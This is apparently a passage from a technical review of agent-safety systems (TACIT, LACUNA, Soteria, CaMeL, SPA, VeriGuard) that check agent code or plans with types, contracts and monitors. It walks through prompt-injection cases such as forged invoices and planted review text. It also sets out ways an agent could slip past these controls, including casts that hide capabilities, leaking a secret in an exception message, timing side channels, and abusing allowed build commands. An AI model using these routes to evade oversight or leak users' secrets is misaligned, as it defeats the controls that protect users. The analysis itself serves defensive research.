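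*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) presents TACIT, a system that uses a version of Scala 3 whose types track capabilities. Instead of calling tools directly, an agent submits snippets of Scala to a server, which runs each snippet only if it compiles. Existing agents such as Claude Code can connect to the server without modification.

### Capture sets and local purity

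A capability is a program value that code must hold to use a resource. In TACIT, a `FileSystem` value gives access to one directory and everything below it, and a `Network` value gives access to a list of hosts. Agent code can't make these values itself and has to request them from TACIT's library.

Capabilities date from the 1960s, but most systems that use them check them only at run time. Scala's capture checking records them in types. Each type has a capture set, which lists the capabilities that a value of that type may use. For example, if `f` is a capability for a file, then the function

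```
(s: String) => f.write(s)
```

has the type `String ->{f} Unit`. The capture set is `{f}`, and `Unit`, as in Lean, carries no information. The plain arrow in `String -> Unit` stands for an empty capture set. A function of that type is pure: it can compute with its argument, but it can't write to a file, use the network or print. Like `noRemoval`, capture checking counts branches that never run.

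A library can now require a pure function at one point in a program and allow effects everywhere else. Odersky and colleagues call this local purity, and it lets an agent work with secrets that it must not reveal.

### Working with a secret the agent cannot read

TACIT's library puts the contents of protected files in a wrapper:

```
trait Classified[+T]:
  def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

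Here `T` is the type of the contents. The method `map` applies a function to them and wraps the result again. The agent has no method for taking the contents out. Suppose a protected file contains a password for an online service, with some stray spaces around it:

```
val key  = readClassified("/data/secrets/key.txt")
val tidy = key.map(k => k.trim)
```

The function `k => k.trim` uses no capabilities, so its type is `String -> String` and the compiler accepts it. If the agent prints `tidy`, it gets `Classified(****)`, while the user's terminal shows the password. The agent can't find out the password's length either, because `key.map(k => k.length)` is also a wrapped value.

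Now suppose the agent tries to copy the password to an ordinary file, for which it holds the capability `outFile`:

```
key.map(k => outFile.write(k))
```

This function has the type `String ->{outFile} Unit`, but `map` requires a function with an empty capture set. The compiler reports that `outFile` "cannot flow into capture set {}", and none of the code runs. The compiler only has to compare two types, whereas taint analysis would have to trace the password through the program.

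In one experiment, an agent wrote almost exactly this code to save confidential recommendations. The destination was in a directory of secrets, so the agent may have been trying to do something legitimate the wrong way. The library has a separate method, `writeClassified`, for saving wrapped data to a protected file.

Ordinary code can trim a string, but summarizing a confidential contract takes a language model. TACIT assumes that the model behind the agent runs in the cloud and may be hostile. The library therefore offers a function, `chat`, that passes wrapped text to a separate, trusted model and wraps the reply. The agent can have the contract summarized and the summary saved without seeing either text. The compiler treats `chat` as pure but can't check that the trusted model's server deletes the text afterwards, so whoever sets up the server has to guarantee that.

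### Keeping a capability after its scope ends

An agent gets access to files for the duration of a block of code. The function `requestFileSystem` creates a capability, passes it to the block, and withdraws it when the block finishes. An agent might try to keep it for longer:

```
val readLater = requestFileSystem("/data") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("secret.txt").read()
}
readLater()
```

The block returns a function that would read the file later, after the permission has ended. The type of that function is `() ->{fs} String`. The type of the block's result has to make sense outside the block, where `fs` doesn't exist, so the result has no valid type and the compiler rejects the program. The same rule prevents the agent from hiding the capability in a list or in a variable outside the block. The compiler accepts a block that reads an ordinary file and returns the text, because a string contains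 no capabilities.

Types control when the agent can use files, but the library checks which files at run time and rejects any path outside `/data`. The library checks network hosts and the names of external commands in the same way.

### Why casts and reflection have to go

All of this depends on capture sets being accurate, and ordinary Scala has features that can make them wrong. A cast tells the compiler to treat a value as having a different type, without checking:

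```
val leak = (k: String) => outFile.write(k)
key.map(leak.asInstanceOf[String -> Unit])
```

The cast removes `outFile` from the type, but the function still writes to the file. Reflection is just as dangerous because it lets a running program look up classes and methods by name, and the type checker treats the name as an ordinary string. A function with an empty capture set could therefore find a method that writes files.

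TACIT therefore compiles agent code in safe mode, a subset of Scala that excludes unchecked casts, reflection, and global functions whose types hide their effects, such as the ordinary `println`. Safe mode arrived as an experimental feature in Scala 3.8.3 (Mazur, *Scala 3.8.3 is now available!*). Scala's documentation describes capture checking itself as "still highly experimental and unstable".

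Library code that opens files and sends mail can't be written in safe mode, so programmers mark it `@assumeSafe` and take responsibility for it. Scala's *Safe Mode* gives the example of a mailer that shows each message to the user and sends it only if the user agrees. Agent code can call this mailer but not the unrestricted one underneath. If the programmer forgot to ask for the user's agreement, the compiler would still accept the code.

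Safe mode does not track exceptions, the errors that interrupt a program, because almost any operation can cause one. A function passed to `map` could therefore leak the password by throwing an exception with the password in its message. TACIT handles this at run time by catching exceptions and wrapping or hiding their contents.

Computer-checked proofs exist for the core of capture checking, but Odersky and colleagues note that a further argument is needed to show that safe mode provides the purity it promises. For now, users have to trust, in part, that the compiler's programmers were careful.

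### How TACIT did in tests

The main safety test uses a software project with a directory of passwords, a database and confidential documents. Odersky and colleagues paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 prompt injections, for 120 trials. In another 11 trials, the user asked for the secrets directly or pretended to be someone entitled to them, such as an administrator replacing passwords in an emergency. Each model did all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets in `Classified` wrappers and once with the secrets as plain strings. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

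| Model | Secure with wrappers | Secure without | Tasks completed with wrappers | Tasks completed without |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 100% | 98.5% | 99.2% | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 100% | 91.6% | 90.0% | 88.3% |

The perfect scores are expected from the design, since an agent can't repeat text it never received. They show only that 10 attacks exposed no hole in the implementation. Prompt injection accounts for little of the difference between the columns. Without wrappers, Claude Sonnet 4.6 resisted all 120 injections but gave in to two of the 11 malicious users, while MiniMax M2.5 gave in to three injections and eight malicious users. It's also unclear whether wrappers help agents complete more tasks. Odersky and colleagues suggest that Claude's low score without wrappers may be an artefact, because Claude often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

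They also adapted AgentDojo, a standard benchmark for prompt injection. Across four domains and two models, one of 1,926 attacks succeeded. In that case, the user asked for a room at one hotel, and the attacker inserted a recommendation for another hotel into the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews in full, including the recommendation. AgentDojo counts this as a success for the attacker because the other hotel's name appears in the answer. The policy allowed the agent to show public reviews to the user, so it is hard to call this a failure of the type system.

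The type system seems to protect the user less in AgentDojo than in the main test. The published signatures of tools such as `sendMoney` require no capability, and the agent's instructions warn that side effects inside `map` happen immediately. An agent can apparently send money from inside a supposedly pure function, and it may have to do so to pay a bill that it can't read. The user is protected mostly because the agent writes its code without seeing the injected text, as in Meijer's email example. If a helper model reads the payee's account number from a forged bill, the money could still go to the forger.

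Security reduced task completion on some of these tasks. With the model o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 52.9% of the office tasks, compared with 81.4% for CaMeL, a system that tracks data at run time. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, the two systems had similar completion rates on office tasks, and TACIT did far better on travel tasks.

Agents performed about as well writing Scala as they did with ordinary tool calling. On τ²-bench, which simulates customer service for an airline and a shop, all three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT. Odersky and colleagues credit the typed results and the compiler's error messages. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software issues, MiniMax M2.5 resolved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without, a difference of five issues. Depending on the model and domain, between 0.3% and 7.9% of the snippets on τ²-bench failed to compile at first, and those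 needed fewer than 1.4 retries on average. Many of the errors were unrelated to safety. For example, agents often forgot to double the dollar sign in a Scala string.

The reusable part of the library is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and each new set of tools takes up to a few hundred more. Other languages could support something similar. In *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026), Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova use security libraries for Haskell, and the compiler applies the same policies to the agent's code and to the developer's code around it. They suggest adding types for permissions that a program can use only once. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) conjectures that such checks would combine well with run-time tracking, which can handle behaviour that the compiler can't determine in advance.

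### What TACIT leaves out

A snippet that compiles can still give the wrong answer. TACIT would accept an agent that summarizes the wrong contract or books a flight for the wrong day, as long as it uses only the capabilities it has.

Code can also leak secrets through timing. A pure function can't print the password, but it can run for a long time if the first letter is `a` and finish at once if it isn't. An agent that measures the delay can learn whether the first letter is `a`, then repeat the process for other letters. Preventing this would require control over how long programs run, which capture sets don't describe.

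External processes are probably the most serious exclusion in practice. The Scala compiler cannot control what another program does once an agent starts it, so the only protection left is the list of permitted commands. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only specific safe commands, such as `git diff` and `sbt`. But `sbt` is a build tool that runs code from the project's build files, which a coding agent can often edit. They also recommend a sandbox, which confines a process to certain files and network addresses, for security-critical deployments. A sandbox alone would not have protected the password, because an agent may be allowed both to read a file and to contact its cloud model, and it leaks the password by doing one after the other.

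### LACUNA: code that the model writes while the program runs

TACIT's snippets come from an ordinary agent loop outside the Scala program. Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, from the same group, put the request to the model inside the program:

```
def agent[T](task: String): T
```

Programmers call a gap like this a typed hole, because the missing code has a known type. When execution reaches the hole, the model receives the task, the type `T`, the surrounding source code and a list of the available variables. It replies with Scala code, which the compiler checks as if a programmer had written it at that point. If the code has the right type, it runs. Otherwise the model gets the error messages and tries again, up to a retry limit.

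In an example from the paper, a variable `balance` contains 100, and the program asks for a whole number with the task "subtract 50 and return the new balance". The model writes:

```
balance -= 50
s"remaining: $balance"
```

The second line is a string, not a number, so the compiler rejects both lines and `balance` stays at 100. An interpreter that detected the error only when it reached the second line would already have changed `balance`.

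A snippet with the right types can still subtract 50 and then divide by zero, and the subtraction is not undone. Snippets can also call `agent` themselves, which is how LACUNA represents loops and teams of agents. The code for an inner call doesn't exist until the outer snippet is running, so if the model never generates an acceptable inner snippet, the outer snippet's earlier effects remain.

LACUNA can use capture checking too, so code that fills a hole can use only the capabilities available there. With TACIT's `map`, the agent normally has to write the function for a secret without having seen the secret. Capture checking allows LACUNA to put a hole in that function, which a trusted local model fills after reading the secret. The compiler still requires the new code to be pure.

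LACUNA's results are more mixed than TACIT's. On BrowseComp-Plus, a benchmark of difficult research questions, the compiler rejected 8.6% of DeepSeek-V4-Flash's snippets, with an average of 0.7 retries per question, and the agent answered 27.1% of the questions correctly. On τ²-bench, the same model solved 76.0% of 392 tasks with LACUNA. The paper calls this "on par" with ordinary tool calling, but it reports 90.0% for tool calling. On the retail tasks, the model solved 58.8% with LACUNA and 80.9% with tool calling. A weaker model, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, solved 29.1% of tasks with LACUNA and 33.2% without it. On one set of telecom tasks, the compiler rejected 89% of the weaker model's snippets.

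TACIT's agents improved slightly on the same benchmark, so types alone probably don't explain LACUNA's loss. LACUNA requires the model to write the control flow of the whole agent, not just the next few tool calls. The experiments also used different models and settings, with reasoning switched off for LACUNA.

On the AgentDojo benchmark, eight of 1,898 attacks succeeded against LACUNA. Zhao and colleagues point out that capture checking enforces the limits set at each hole, but the developer has to choose those limits. If a task requires permission to send messages, an attacker may be able to persuade the model to send the wrong message.

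They also state that well-typed code can be wrong. For the task above, the model could have written `balance += 50` and then returned `balance`. The result is a whole number, so the compiler accepts it, and the retry loop never starts because it responds only to compiler errors. A type that required the result to be exactly 50 less than the starting balance would catch this mistake, and they propose such types as future work. But somebody would then have to state the requirement for each task, which TACIT and LACUNA were designed to avoid.

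### Checking each token instead of the finished program

TACIT and LACUNA check a snippet after the model finishes it. In *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models*, Mündler, He and colleagues (2025) instead prevent the model from writing ill-typed code. A language model produces text in short pieces called tokens. At each step it assigns a probability to every possible next token, and ordinary software picks one. Their method checks each chosen token. If no well-typed program begins with the code so far plus that token, the software sets the token's probability to zero and picks again.

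In one example, a model writing TypeScript has reached `parseInt(num`, where `num` is a number but `parseInt` expects a string. Without type checking during generation, CodeLlama 34B continues with `, 10)`, which doesn't compile. The type checker can't reject `num` immediately, because the expression may be unfinished. It searches for operations that lead from a number to a string, such as `.toString()`, and allows only continuations that can produce a string. The model then writes `num.toString()`.

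An ordinary compiler expects complete programs and can't check code that is still being generated, so Mündler and colleagues wrote about 11,000 lines of Python to do this for part of TypeScript. Their method more than halved compilation errors, and the share of programs that passed their tests rose by about 3.5% in relative terms. Generation took 39% to 52% longer.

Biagiola, Cesario and colleagues (2026), in *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation*, tested the same tool and got the opposite result. Across six models, programs written without the tool were more often correct. On one benchmark, Qwen2.5-32B solved 82.3% of the problems without it and 72.3% with it. The tool rejects some valid programs, including any that call a function before defining it. In one case, the model began to write `isPalindrome`, a function it was going to define later in the program. The tool allowed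 only names that already existed, so after `is` the model had to continue with `isNaN`, which tests whether something is not a number. The program compiled but did the wrong thing. In other cases, the model repeated itself until it ran out of time.

The two results are compatible because the experiments used the check differently. Mündler and colleagues kept every program that compiled without it and applied it only to new attempts at the others, so it could fix failed programs without breaking working ones. Biagiola and colleagues applied it to every program from the start. The check looks worthwhile as a fallback, but using it all the time does harm unless it accepts nearly everything that the real compiler accepts.

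That condition is much easier to meet for a small language. When Biagiola and colleagues used a complete syntax check for TOML, a simple configuration file format, every model improved, by 2.5% for a large one and up to 54% for a small one. A plan in JSON, or in a small language like `Script`, is closer to TOML than to TypeScript, so token-by-token checking seems better suited to plans than to general code. Some model providers already use it to guarantee that output follows a given JSON format.

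For general code, rejection after generation has two practical advantages. It works with any model, whereas token-by-token checking needs the probabilities of all possible tokens, which commercial providers usually don't reveal. It also produces an error message. *Generative Compilation* (2026) points out that silently replacing a token gives the model no information about what was wrong, and that the model may already be committed to a bad design. As a compromise, that paper proposes filling the unfinished parts of a Rust program with placeholders, so that an ordinary compiler can check it and report errors while the model is still writing. *AGDecode* (2026) instead extends token-by-token checks from types to facts about values, such as that a divisor isn't zero.

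If the model is untrusted, the verifier has to check the finished program, even if it was already checked during generation. Whoever runs the model controls how it picks tokens, and could skip the earlier check or do it badly. Even when run as intended, the tool that Biagiola and colleagues tested let through invalid programs in 0.69% of cases, not counting timeouts.

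## Checking whole plans against contracts and policies

TACIT's compiler controls which tools a program can use, but not in what order or under what circumstances. An airline's agent with the capability to change bookings could cancel and refund a trip after the customer has taken the outbound flight, and the program would still compile. To prevent this, a verifier has to compare the whole sequence of calls with the airline's rules.

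### Safety and liveness

A safety property requires that something bad never happens, such as the agent canceling a reservation without first checking whether the customer has flown. A violation occurs at a particular call, and nothing the agent does afterwards can undo it. A monitor can enforce the property by blocking that call.

A liveness property requires that something eventually happens, for example that an agent reads a file back after writing it to check the contents. As with the earlier rule about incident tickets, no single call violates this property, so a monitor can't report a violation until the agent stops. A verifier with the complete plan can check in advance that every path includes the read. If every path ends, "eventually" means "before the end", so the verifier can check both kinds of property by examining the calls on each path.

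### Following a plan from state to state

He, Desai and colleagues (2026), in *SOTERIA*, present a system that does this. A language model drafts contracts for the tools and formal versions of the written policies, and people correct the drafts, which took a few hours for each of three domains. The planner, also a language model, then writes each plan in a small language of states and transitions. In the main example, a customer wants to cancel a reservation, and the airline has two rules:

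1. Before cancelling, the agent must check that the customer has not taken any of the flights.
2. The agent may cancel only within 24 hours of booking.

The planner proposes this plan, shown here in simplified notation:

```
LOOKUP:       resv = get_reservation(rid)              → CHECK_AGE
CHECK_AGE:    hours = hours_between(resv.booked, now)  → CHECK_RULES
CHECK_RULES:  if hours ≤ 24                            → CANCEL
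              otherwise                                → REFUSE
CANCEL:       result = cancel_reservation(rid)         → DONE
```

`DONE` and `REFUSE` end the plan. Necula and Lee's generator worked backwards from the last line of a program, but Soteria works forwards from the first state. For each state it computes a formula, called the symbolic state, that describes every combination of values the variables could have when the plan gets there. A transition carries the formula forward like this:

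```
facts at the next state =
    facts at this state
    and  the condition on the branch
    and  the postcondition of the tool, if the transition calls one
```

For the cancellation plan, this gives:

| State | Facts on arrival |
|---|---|
| `LOOKUP` | `rid` is a valid reservation number |
| `CHECK_AGE` | also, `resv` is the record for `rid` |
| `CHECK_RULES` | also, `hours` is the time since booking |
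| `CANCEL` | also, `hours ≤ 24` |
| `REFUSE` | the facts at `CHECK_RULES`, and `hours > 24` |

If several transitions lead to the same state, the verifier joins their formulas with "or". A fuller version of the plan also allows cancellation for business-class tickets and for insured customers who are ill, so its formula for `CANCEL` requires at least one of these reasons to apply.

The verifier can now check each tool's precondition. For the call in `CANCEL`, the verification condition is:

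```
facts at CANCEL  implies  precondition of cancel_reservation
```

Suppose the tool requires an existing reservation. This condition holds because one of the facts is that `resv` is the record for `rid`. Soteria passes such conditions to Dafny.

The verifier also checks that the plan can't get stuck. The facts at each state must be satisfiable, since otherwise no run could reach that state. They must also imply that at least one outgoing branch is open. If the planner had written `hours < 24` on one branch and `hours > 24` on the other, a booking exactly 24 hours old would satisfy neither condition.

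### The missing flown-status check

The plan passes all these checks although it breaks the airline's first rule. Contracts can't detect the problem because each one concerns a single call, and the airline's software carries out a cancellation whether or not anyone has checked the flights. The rule depends on earlier calls, so the verifier needs a record of them.

During verification, Soteria therefore adds variables that the real plan doesn't have. A counter numbers the calls, and a log for each relevant tool stores the number, arguments and result of every call to it. The first rule then becomes a statement about two logs, which must be true wherever the plan ends:

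```
for every entry c in the log of cancel_reservation
  there is an entry f in the log of no_flights_flown with
    f.step < c.step  and  f.rid = c.rid  and  f.result = true
```

On the path to `REFUSE`, the cancellation log is empty, so the statement is trivially true. On the path to `DONE`, the cancellation log has one entry and the other log is empty, so no suitable `f` exists and Dafny reports an error. Soteria then rejects the plan and sends the planner a message that identifies the rule.

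The planner can repair the plan by adding two states after the lookup:

```
LOOKUP:       resv = get_reservation(rid)   → CHECK_FLOWN
CHECK_FLOWN:  ok = no_flights_flown(rid)    → FLOWN_RULE
FLOWN_RULE:   if ok                         → CHECK_AGE
              otherwise                     → REFUSE
```

With the calls numbered from 0, the check is now call 1 and the cancellation is call 3. Both use the same `rid`, and the result of the check must be `true` because the plan reaches `CANCEL` only in the branch that requires `ok`. If the planner added the check but ignored its result, the log could contain `false`, and Dafny would reject the plan again.

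Some rules concern where a value comes from. For example, a refund amount must depend on the reservation. To check these rules, the verifier keeps a set of sources for every variable and updates it at each assignment. This shows that the amount depends on the reservation, but not that the amount is correct, since ten times the ticket price has the same source as the ticket price.

Common procedures, such as cancelling or refunding, can be separate sub-plans with their own contracts. Soteria verifies each sub-plan once, and larger plans can then call it like a tool. On the airline tasks, with up to eight retries per attempt, GPT-5.4-mini produced plans that passed every check in 65 of 68 attempts with sub-plans and 38 of 60 without them. Plans can't jump back to an earlier state, because the verifier has to process the states in order. If the planner runs out of retries, Soteria continues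 with the plan that passed the most checks and relies on a runtime monitor for the remaining checks.

### Soteria's results

He and colleagues tested Soteria with four models on 207 tasks. The τ²-bench benchmark supplied 50 tasks involving airline reservations and 114 involving shop orders. Another benchmark, Toolathlon, supplied the other 43, which involved files, documents and terminal commands. The researchers also ran the same models without any safeguard and with each of three existing runtime safeguards. A task counted as a success if the agent completed it without violating any specification. The table gives Soteria's success rate, with the best alternative's rate in brackets.

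| Model | Airline | Shop | Toolathlon |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4-mini | 60.0% (50.0%) | 35.1% (20.2%) | 11.6% (2.3%) |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 62.0% (36.0%) | 45.6% (38.6%) | 16.3% (2.3%) |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 70.0% (30.0%) | 56.1% (31.6%) | 9.3% (4.7%) |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 88.0% (56.0%) | 90.4% (46.5%) | 18.6% (11.6%) |

Soteria had no violations in any of these tests, while the unprotected models had between 11 and 42 on each benchmark. But this result follows from the design, because the monitor blocks any call that would violate one of 98 formulas, and He and colleagues counted violations of the same 98 formulas. They also corrected some formulas and added missing ones while auditing the results. The perfect score therefore shows that the monitor works as intended, but it doesn't show that the agents followed every rule the airline or shop cares about.

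In one example from He and colleagues, an unprotected agent upgraded a reservation to business class so that it would qualify for cancellation, then cancelled it. They describe this as a workaround that the policy doesn't permit. But the eligibility formula only requires an earlier lookup that shows business class, so an agent that looked up the reservation again after the upgrade would satisfy the formula.

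The success rates depend on the formulas too. The benchmarks' own evaluators judge only whether the agent completed the task, and by that measure Soteria's lead is smaller. On airline tasks, GPT-5.4-mini completed 60% both with Soteria and with the best alternative. On Toolathlon, Claude Opus 4.6 completed 18.6% with Soteria and 30.2% without any safeguard. When the formulas count towards success, Soteria leads on Toolathlon only because the unprotected agent often broke rules, such as the requirement to read a file back after writing it.

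The largest improvement, for Opus on the shop tasks, appears on both measures, but it came mostly from Opus making required changes more often, not from preventing harm. Without a plan, Opus was often too cautious. In one task it made 11 calls to identify the customer, the order and the product, then handed the conversation to a human instead of making the exchange. It made the required change in 57% of the tasks that needed one. With Soteria, the plan specified when to act, and Opus made the change in all of them.

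Soteria writes a new plan at each turn of a conversation, which makes it expensive for customer service. With Opus, an airline task cost about 80 cents using Soteria and 32 cents without a safeguard. With GPT-5.4-mini, it cost 12.5 cents using Soteria and 3.1 cents without a safeguard. Toolathlon tasks need only one plan, and with Opus a task cost 43 cents using Soteria and 97 cents without it, because the plan avoided many unnecessary steps.

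### Why verified plans still led to violations

He and colleagues also added Soteria's parts one at a time on the airline tasks:

| Configuration | Violations, GPT-5.4-mini | Violations, Gemini 3 Flash | Success, GPT-5.4-mini | Success, Gemini 3 Flash |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Plan without verification | 13 | 27 | 44% | 32% |
| With static verification | 10 | 24 | 46% | 32% |
| With sub-plans as well | 12 | 22 | 50% | 38% |
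| With the runtime monitor as well | 0 | 0 | 60% | 62% |

Static verification alone prevented only three violations with each model, possibly in part because some plans never passed verification. But GPT-5.4-mini still committed 12 violations with sub-plans, which allow nearly all of its plans to pass.

The more likely explanation is that a language model carries out the plan. The model receives the plan as a flowchart, which Soteria shortens as results arrive, but it can still call any tool. The proof covers every run that follows the plan, but the model doesn't always follow it. In Meijer's design, by contrast, an interpreter runs the verified program directly.

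Soteria's monitor makes up for this by checking each call before it runs. It adds the proposed call to the list of calls so far and evaluates the formulas on that list. This needs no solver, because all the values are now known. If the agent tries to cancel before checking the flights, the monitor blocks the call and returns an instruction to check the flights first. The monitor tests liveness properties when the agent finishes. If a tool's result violates its own postcondition, Soteria stops the run, because the proofs about the plan relied on a false contract.

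Soteria also has a strict mode, which allows only the calls that the plan permits in its current state. Suppose a customer asks to cancel one reservation and look up another, but the plan covers only the cancellation. Strict mode blocks the lookup even though it is harmless, while the monitor in ordinary mode allows it because it breaks no rule. The ablation doesn't include strict mode, so it doesn't show how well static verification would work if the agent had to follow the plan.

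The evaluation of Soteria also does not establish how much the proof adds to a good monitor. In five runs of the airline tasks with GPT-5.4-mini and only three planning retries, Soteria succeeded on an average of 50.8% of tasks. AgentSpec, a monitor with no plan, succeeded on 48.0%, and the difference could be due to chance. However, AgentSpec allowed an average of 4.4 violations per run.

### CaMeL and CaMeLoT

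CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind published in 2025, has no model in the position of Soteria's executor. A privileged model reads the user's request and writes a plan in a restricted form of Python, and an interpreter runs it. A second, quarantined model reads untrusted text and extracts information from it, but can't call tools. Nikolaou and colleagues give this example of a plan, slightly simplified:

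```
messages = read_channel_messages("general")
email    = query_ai_assistant("Extract Bob's email from: " + messages)
send_direct_message(email, "Meeting at 3pm")
```

A message in the channel can't add a step to this plan, but it can give a false address for Bob, and the plan will then send the message meant for Bob to the wrong person. To prevent this, CaMeL's interpreter tags every value with where it came from and who may read it. (CaMeL calls the tags capabilities, but unlike TACIT's capabilities they don't give access to anything.) Before each tool call, a policy written as a Python function checks the arguments' tags and allows or denies the call. Here it could deny the call because the address came from an untrusted channel.

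CaMeL applies this policy only when the plan reaches the last line. Nikolaou and colleagues' CaMeLoT makes a similar check before the plan runs. It turns the plan into a finite transition system, a graph of states and the possible steps between them. The plan above has five states: the start, one for each call, and the end. Each state has labels that record which tool the plan is calling, which tools it has already called, and which arguments are trustworthy.

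The rules are in computation tree logic, which has operators for statements about all possible futures. `AG` means "in every state on every path", and `AF` means "at some point on every path". A safety rule for messages and a liveness rule for incident tickets look like this:

```
AG (send_direct_message → recipient_trusted)
AG (create_ticket → AF (resolve_ticket or escalate_ticket))
```

The model checker nuXmv examines every reachable state, which is possible because there are finitely many. For the message plan, it returns a path to a state where the plan calls `send_direct_message` with an untrusted recipient. The planner can repair the plan only if it can get Bob's address from a trusted source, such as the user's request.

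CaMeLoT's model of a plan is coarser than Soteria's. It omits branch conditions, so it treats either branch as possible, and it records that a tool was called but not what the tool returned. A rule could require a flown-status check before a cancellation, but CaMeLoT couldn't tell whether the plan cancels only when the result allows it. The model also assumes that a loop may run any number of times. If a liveness rule requires a plan to close a ticket, and the plan does so after a loop, the model includes a path that repeats the loop forever and never closes the ticket. A model checker has to exclude such paths, or it will reject a plan whose loop always ends in practice.

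Nikolaou and colleagues could express 22 of CaMeL's 28 policies for AgentDojo as rules that CaMeLoT can check in advance. They then ran both systems on the benchmark's 97 ordinary tasks, without any attacks. On 22 tasks, the plan failed to do what the user wanted under both systems. The systems agreed on 59 of the other 75, allowing 42 plans and blocking 17. In most of the disagreements, CaMeL blocked a call for a reason that only emerged during the run, so CaMeLoT leaves CaMeL's runtime checks in place.

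In a second experiment, they took a safe plan for a security operations centre and wrote seven unsafe variants, each breaking a different rule. CaMeLoT detected all seven. A simplified version of CaMeL detected only the one that involved untrusted data. They expected this because they had chosen rules that CaMeL was not designed to express. They also gave a model requests that encouraged bad plans, such as one from a user in a hurry who asked it to skip the approval. CaMeLoT rejected all four of the resulting plans.

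One of the seven rules requires the agent to isolate the infected computer at some point, so a plan that does nothing violates it. Such rules matter when an attacker wants the agent to stop working, because an idle agent satisfies every safety property.

### SPA and data from earlier requests

CaMeL keeps untrusted data away from the planner while one plan runs, but many agents also save results for later. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes an agent that fetches an invoice on Monday and saves its details. On Tuesday the user says "pay the invoice we discussed yesterday". If the agent shows the saved invoice to the planner, any instructions hidden in it can influence the plan. Even if the planner never sees the invoice, the account number in it may belong to an attacker.

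SPA hides saved results from the planner, which sees only descriptions of them: the format of the data, what it represents, and which request produced it. The planner writes a complete plan from six kinds of step. A step can retrieve a saved result, call a tool, have a quarantined model process some text, display something to the user, choose between two branches, or repeat steps for each item in a list. For Tuesday's request the plan might be:

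```
invoice = retrieve(saved_result_1)
pay(account = invoice.account, amount = invoice.amount)
```

Every value has a confidentiality label, which records how secret it is, and an integrity label, which records how far the agent can trust it. When a step combines several values, the result is as secret as the most secret of them and as trustworthy as the least trustworthy. Each tool has a maximum secrecy and a minimum trustworthiness for its inputs. Before the plan runs, a verifier works out the labels step by step and rejects the plan if any call breaks these limits.

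The saved invoice keeps its Monday labels, so `invoice.account` is untrustworthy. If `pay` requires trustworthy inputs, the verifier rejects the plan. Having the quarantined model summarize the invoice wouldn't help, because the summary gets the same labels. Branching on the invoice wouldn't help either. If the plan pays a fixed account only when the invoice is marked urgent, the attacker can't choose the account but can still trigger the payment, so the verifier gives every step inside the branch the low integrity of the condition.

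Unfortunately, a genuine invoice arrives by the same route as a forged one and gets the same labels, so the verifier also rejects the payment that the user wants. Girrens and Wang measured the cost on AgentDojo, and on a version of it in which they split each task into two to five requests:

| Benchmark | Labels checked | Tasks completed without attacks | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|
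| AgentDojo | No | 53.0% | 0.4% |
| AgentDojo | Yes | 29.0% | 0.0% |
| Several requests | No | 62.5% | 0.3% |
| Several requests | Yes | 35.3% | 0.2% |

On the original benchmark, checking the labels stopped the only four of 949 attacks that had succeeded, but nearly halved the number of tasks the agent completed. Most of the protection in this test came from planning first. But the test understates the value of the labels, because its attacks mainly try to give the agent new instructions. Planning first doesn't stop an attacker who changes the account number on an invoice, because that attack needs no new instructions. Girrens and Wang suggest recovering some of the lost tasks by giving separate labels to each field of a record, or by raising a value's integrity after an explicit check.

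SPA has an optional defence against hostile tool descriptions like the one in Meijer's mail example. The planner invents the tools it needs from the user's request alone, and SPA then matches them to real ones. The matching failed in about three quarters of the trials, and the agent completed only 14.1% of tasks even without label checks.

### VeriGuard: verifying the policy instead of the plan

Many agents never write a complete plan. *VeriGuard* (Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues, 2025) handles them by verifying a program that checks individual actions. A language model turns a request in English into a policy function in Python, with a precondition and a postcondition. VeriGuard resolves ambiguities in the request, runs automatically generated tests, and uses the verifier Nagini to prove that the function meets its contract. All this happens before the agent starts. While the agent is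 running, VeriGuard applies the function to each action and intervenes if the function rejects it.

The function needs structured arguments, such as a list of recipients, but an agent's output is often plain text. Another language model therefore extracts the arguments, and the proof doesn't cover this step. An example in VeriGuard's instructions has an email going to alex@example.com and a person named Dona, whose address isn't in the text. The expected output lists dona@example.com as the second recipient. A check on recipients would then use an address that the model had guessed.

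Miculicich and colleagues tested VeriGuard on Agent Security Bench, which includes prompt injections and false entries in an agent's memory. Without a defence, about half to two thirds of the attacks succeeded, depending on the model. VeriGuard stopped every attack, but so did a simpler safeguard that asked a language model whether each action complied with the policy. Agents completed more of their ordinary tasks with VeriGuard, however. With Gemini 2.5 Flash, for instance, they completed 63.3% with VeriGuard and 40.2% with the simpler safeguard.

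Much of that advantage may come from how VeriGuard responds to a violation. Miculicich and colleagues compared five responses with the same model:

| Response to a violation | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| End the whole task | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Block the action | 0.0% | 38.1% |
| Block only the offending tool call | 0.0% | 44.6% |
| Explain the violation and ask for a new plan | 11.9% | 62.1% |
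| Block the tool call and ask for a new plan | 0.0% | 63.3% |

When VeriGuard only blocked actions or calls, its completion rates were close to those of the simpler safeguard. An explanation helped the agent finish its work, but some agents ignored explanations that came without a block.

VeriGuard's results don't show what the formal proof contributes. When Miculicich and colleagues added the parts of VeriGuard one at a time, the share of successful attacks fell to zero before they added verification. A proof could still matter for inputs that neither the tests nor the benchmark include, but measuring that would require attacks designed to find faults in the policy code.

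### Planning before reading the data

Branches let a plan respond to results that the planner can foresee, as in the cancellation plan, but not to surprises. If a user asks an agent to follow the instructions in today's email from their boss, the planner can't list useful steps until someone reads the email.

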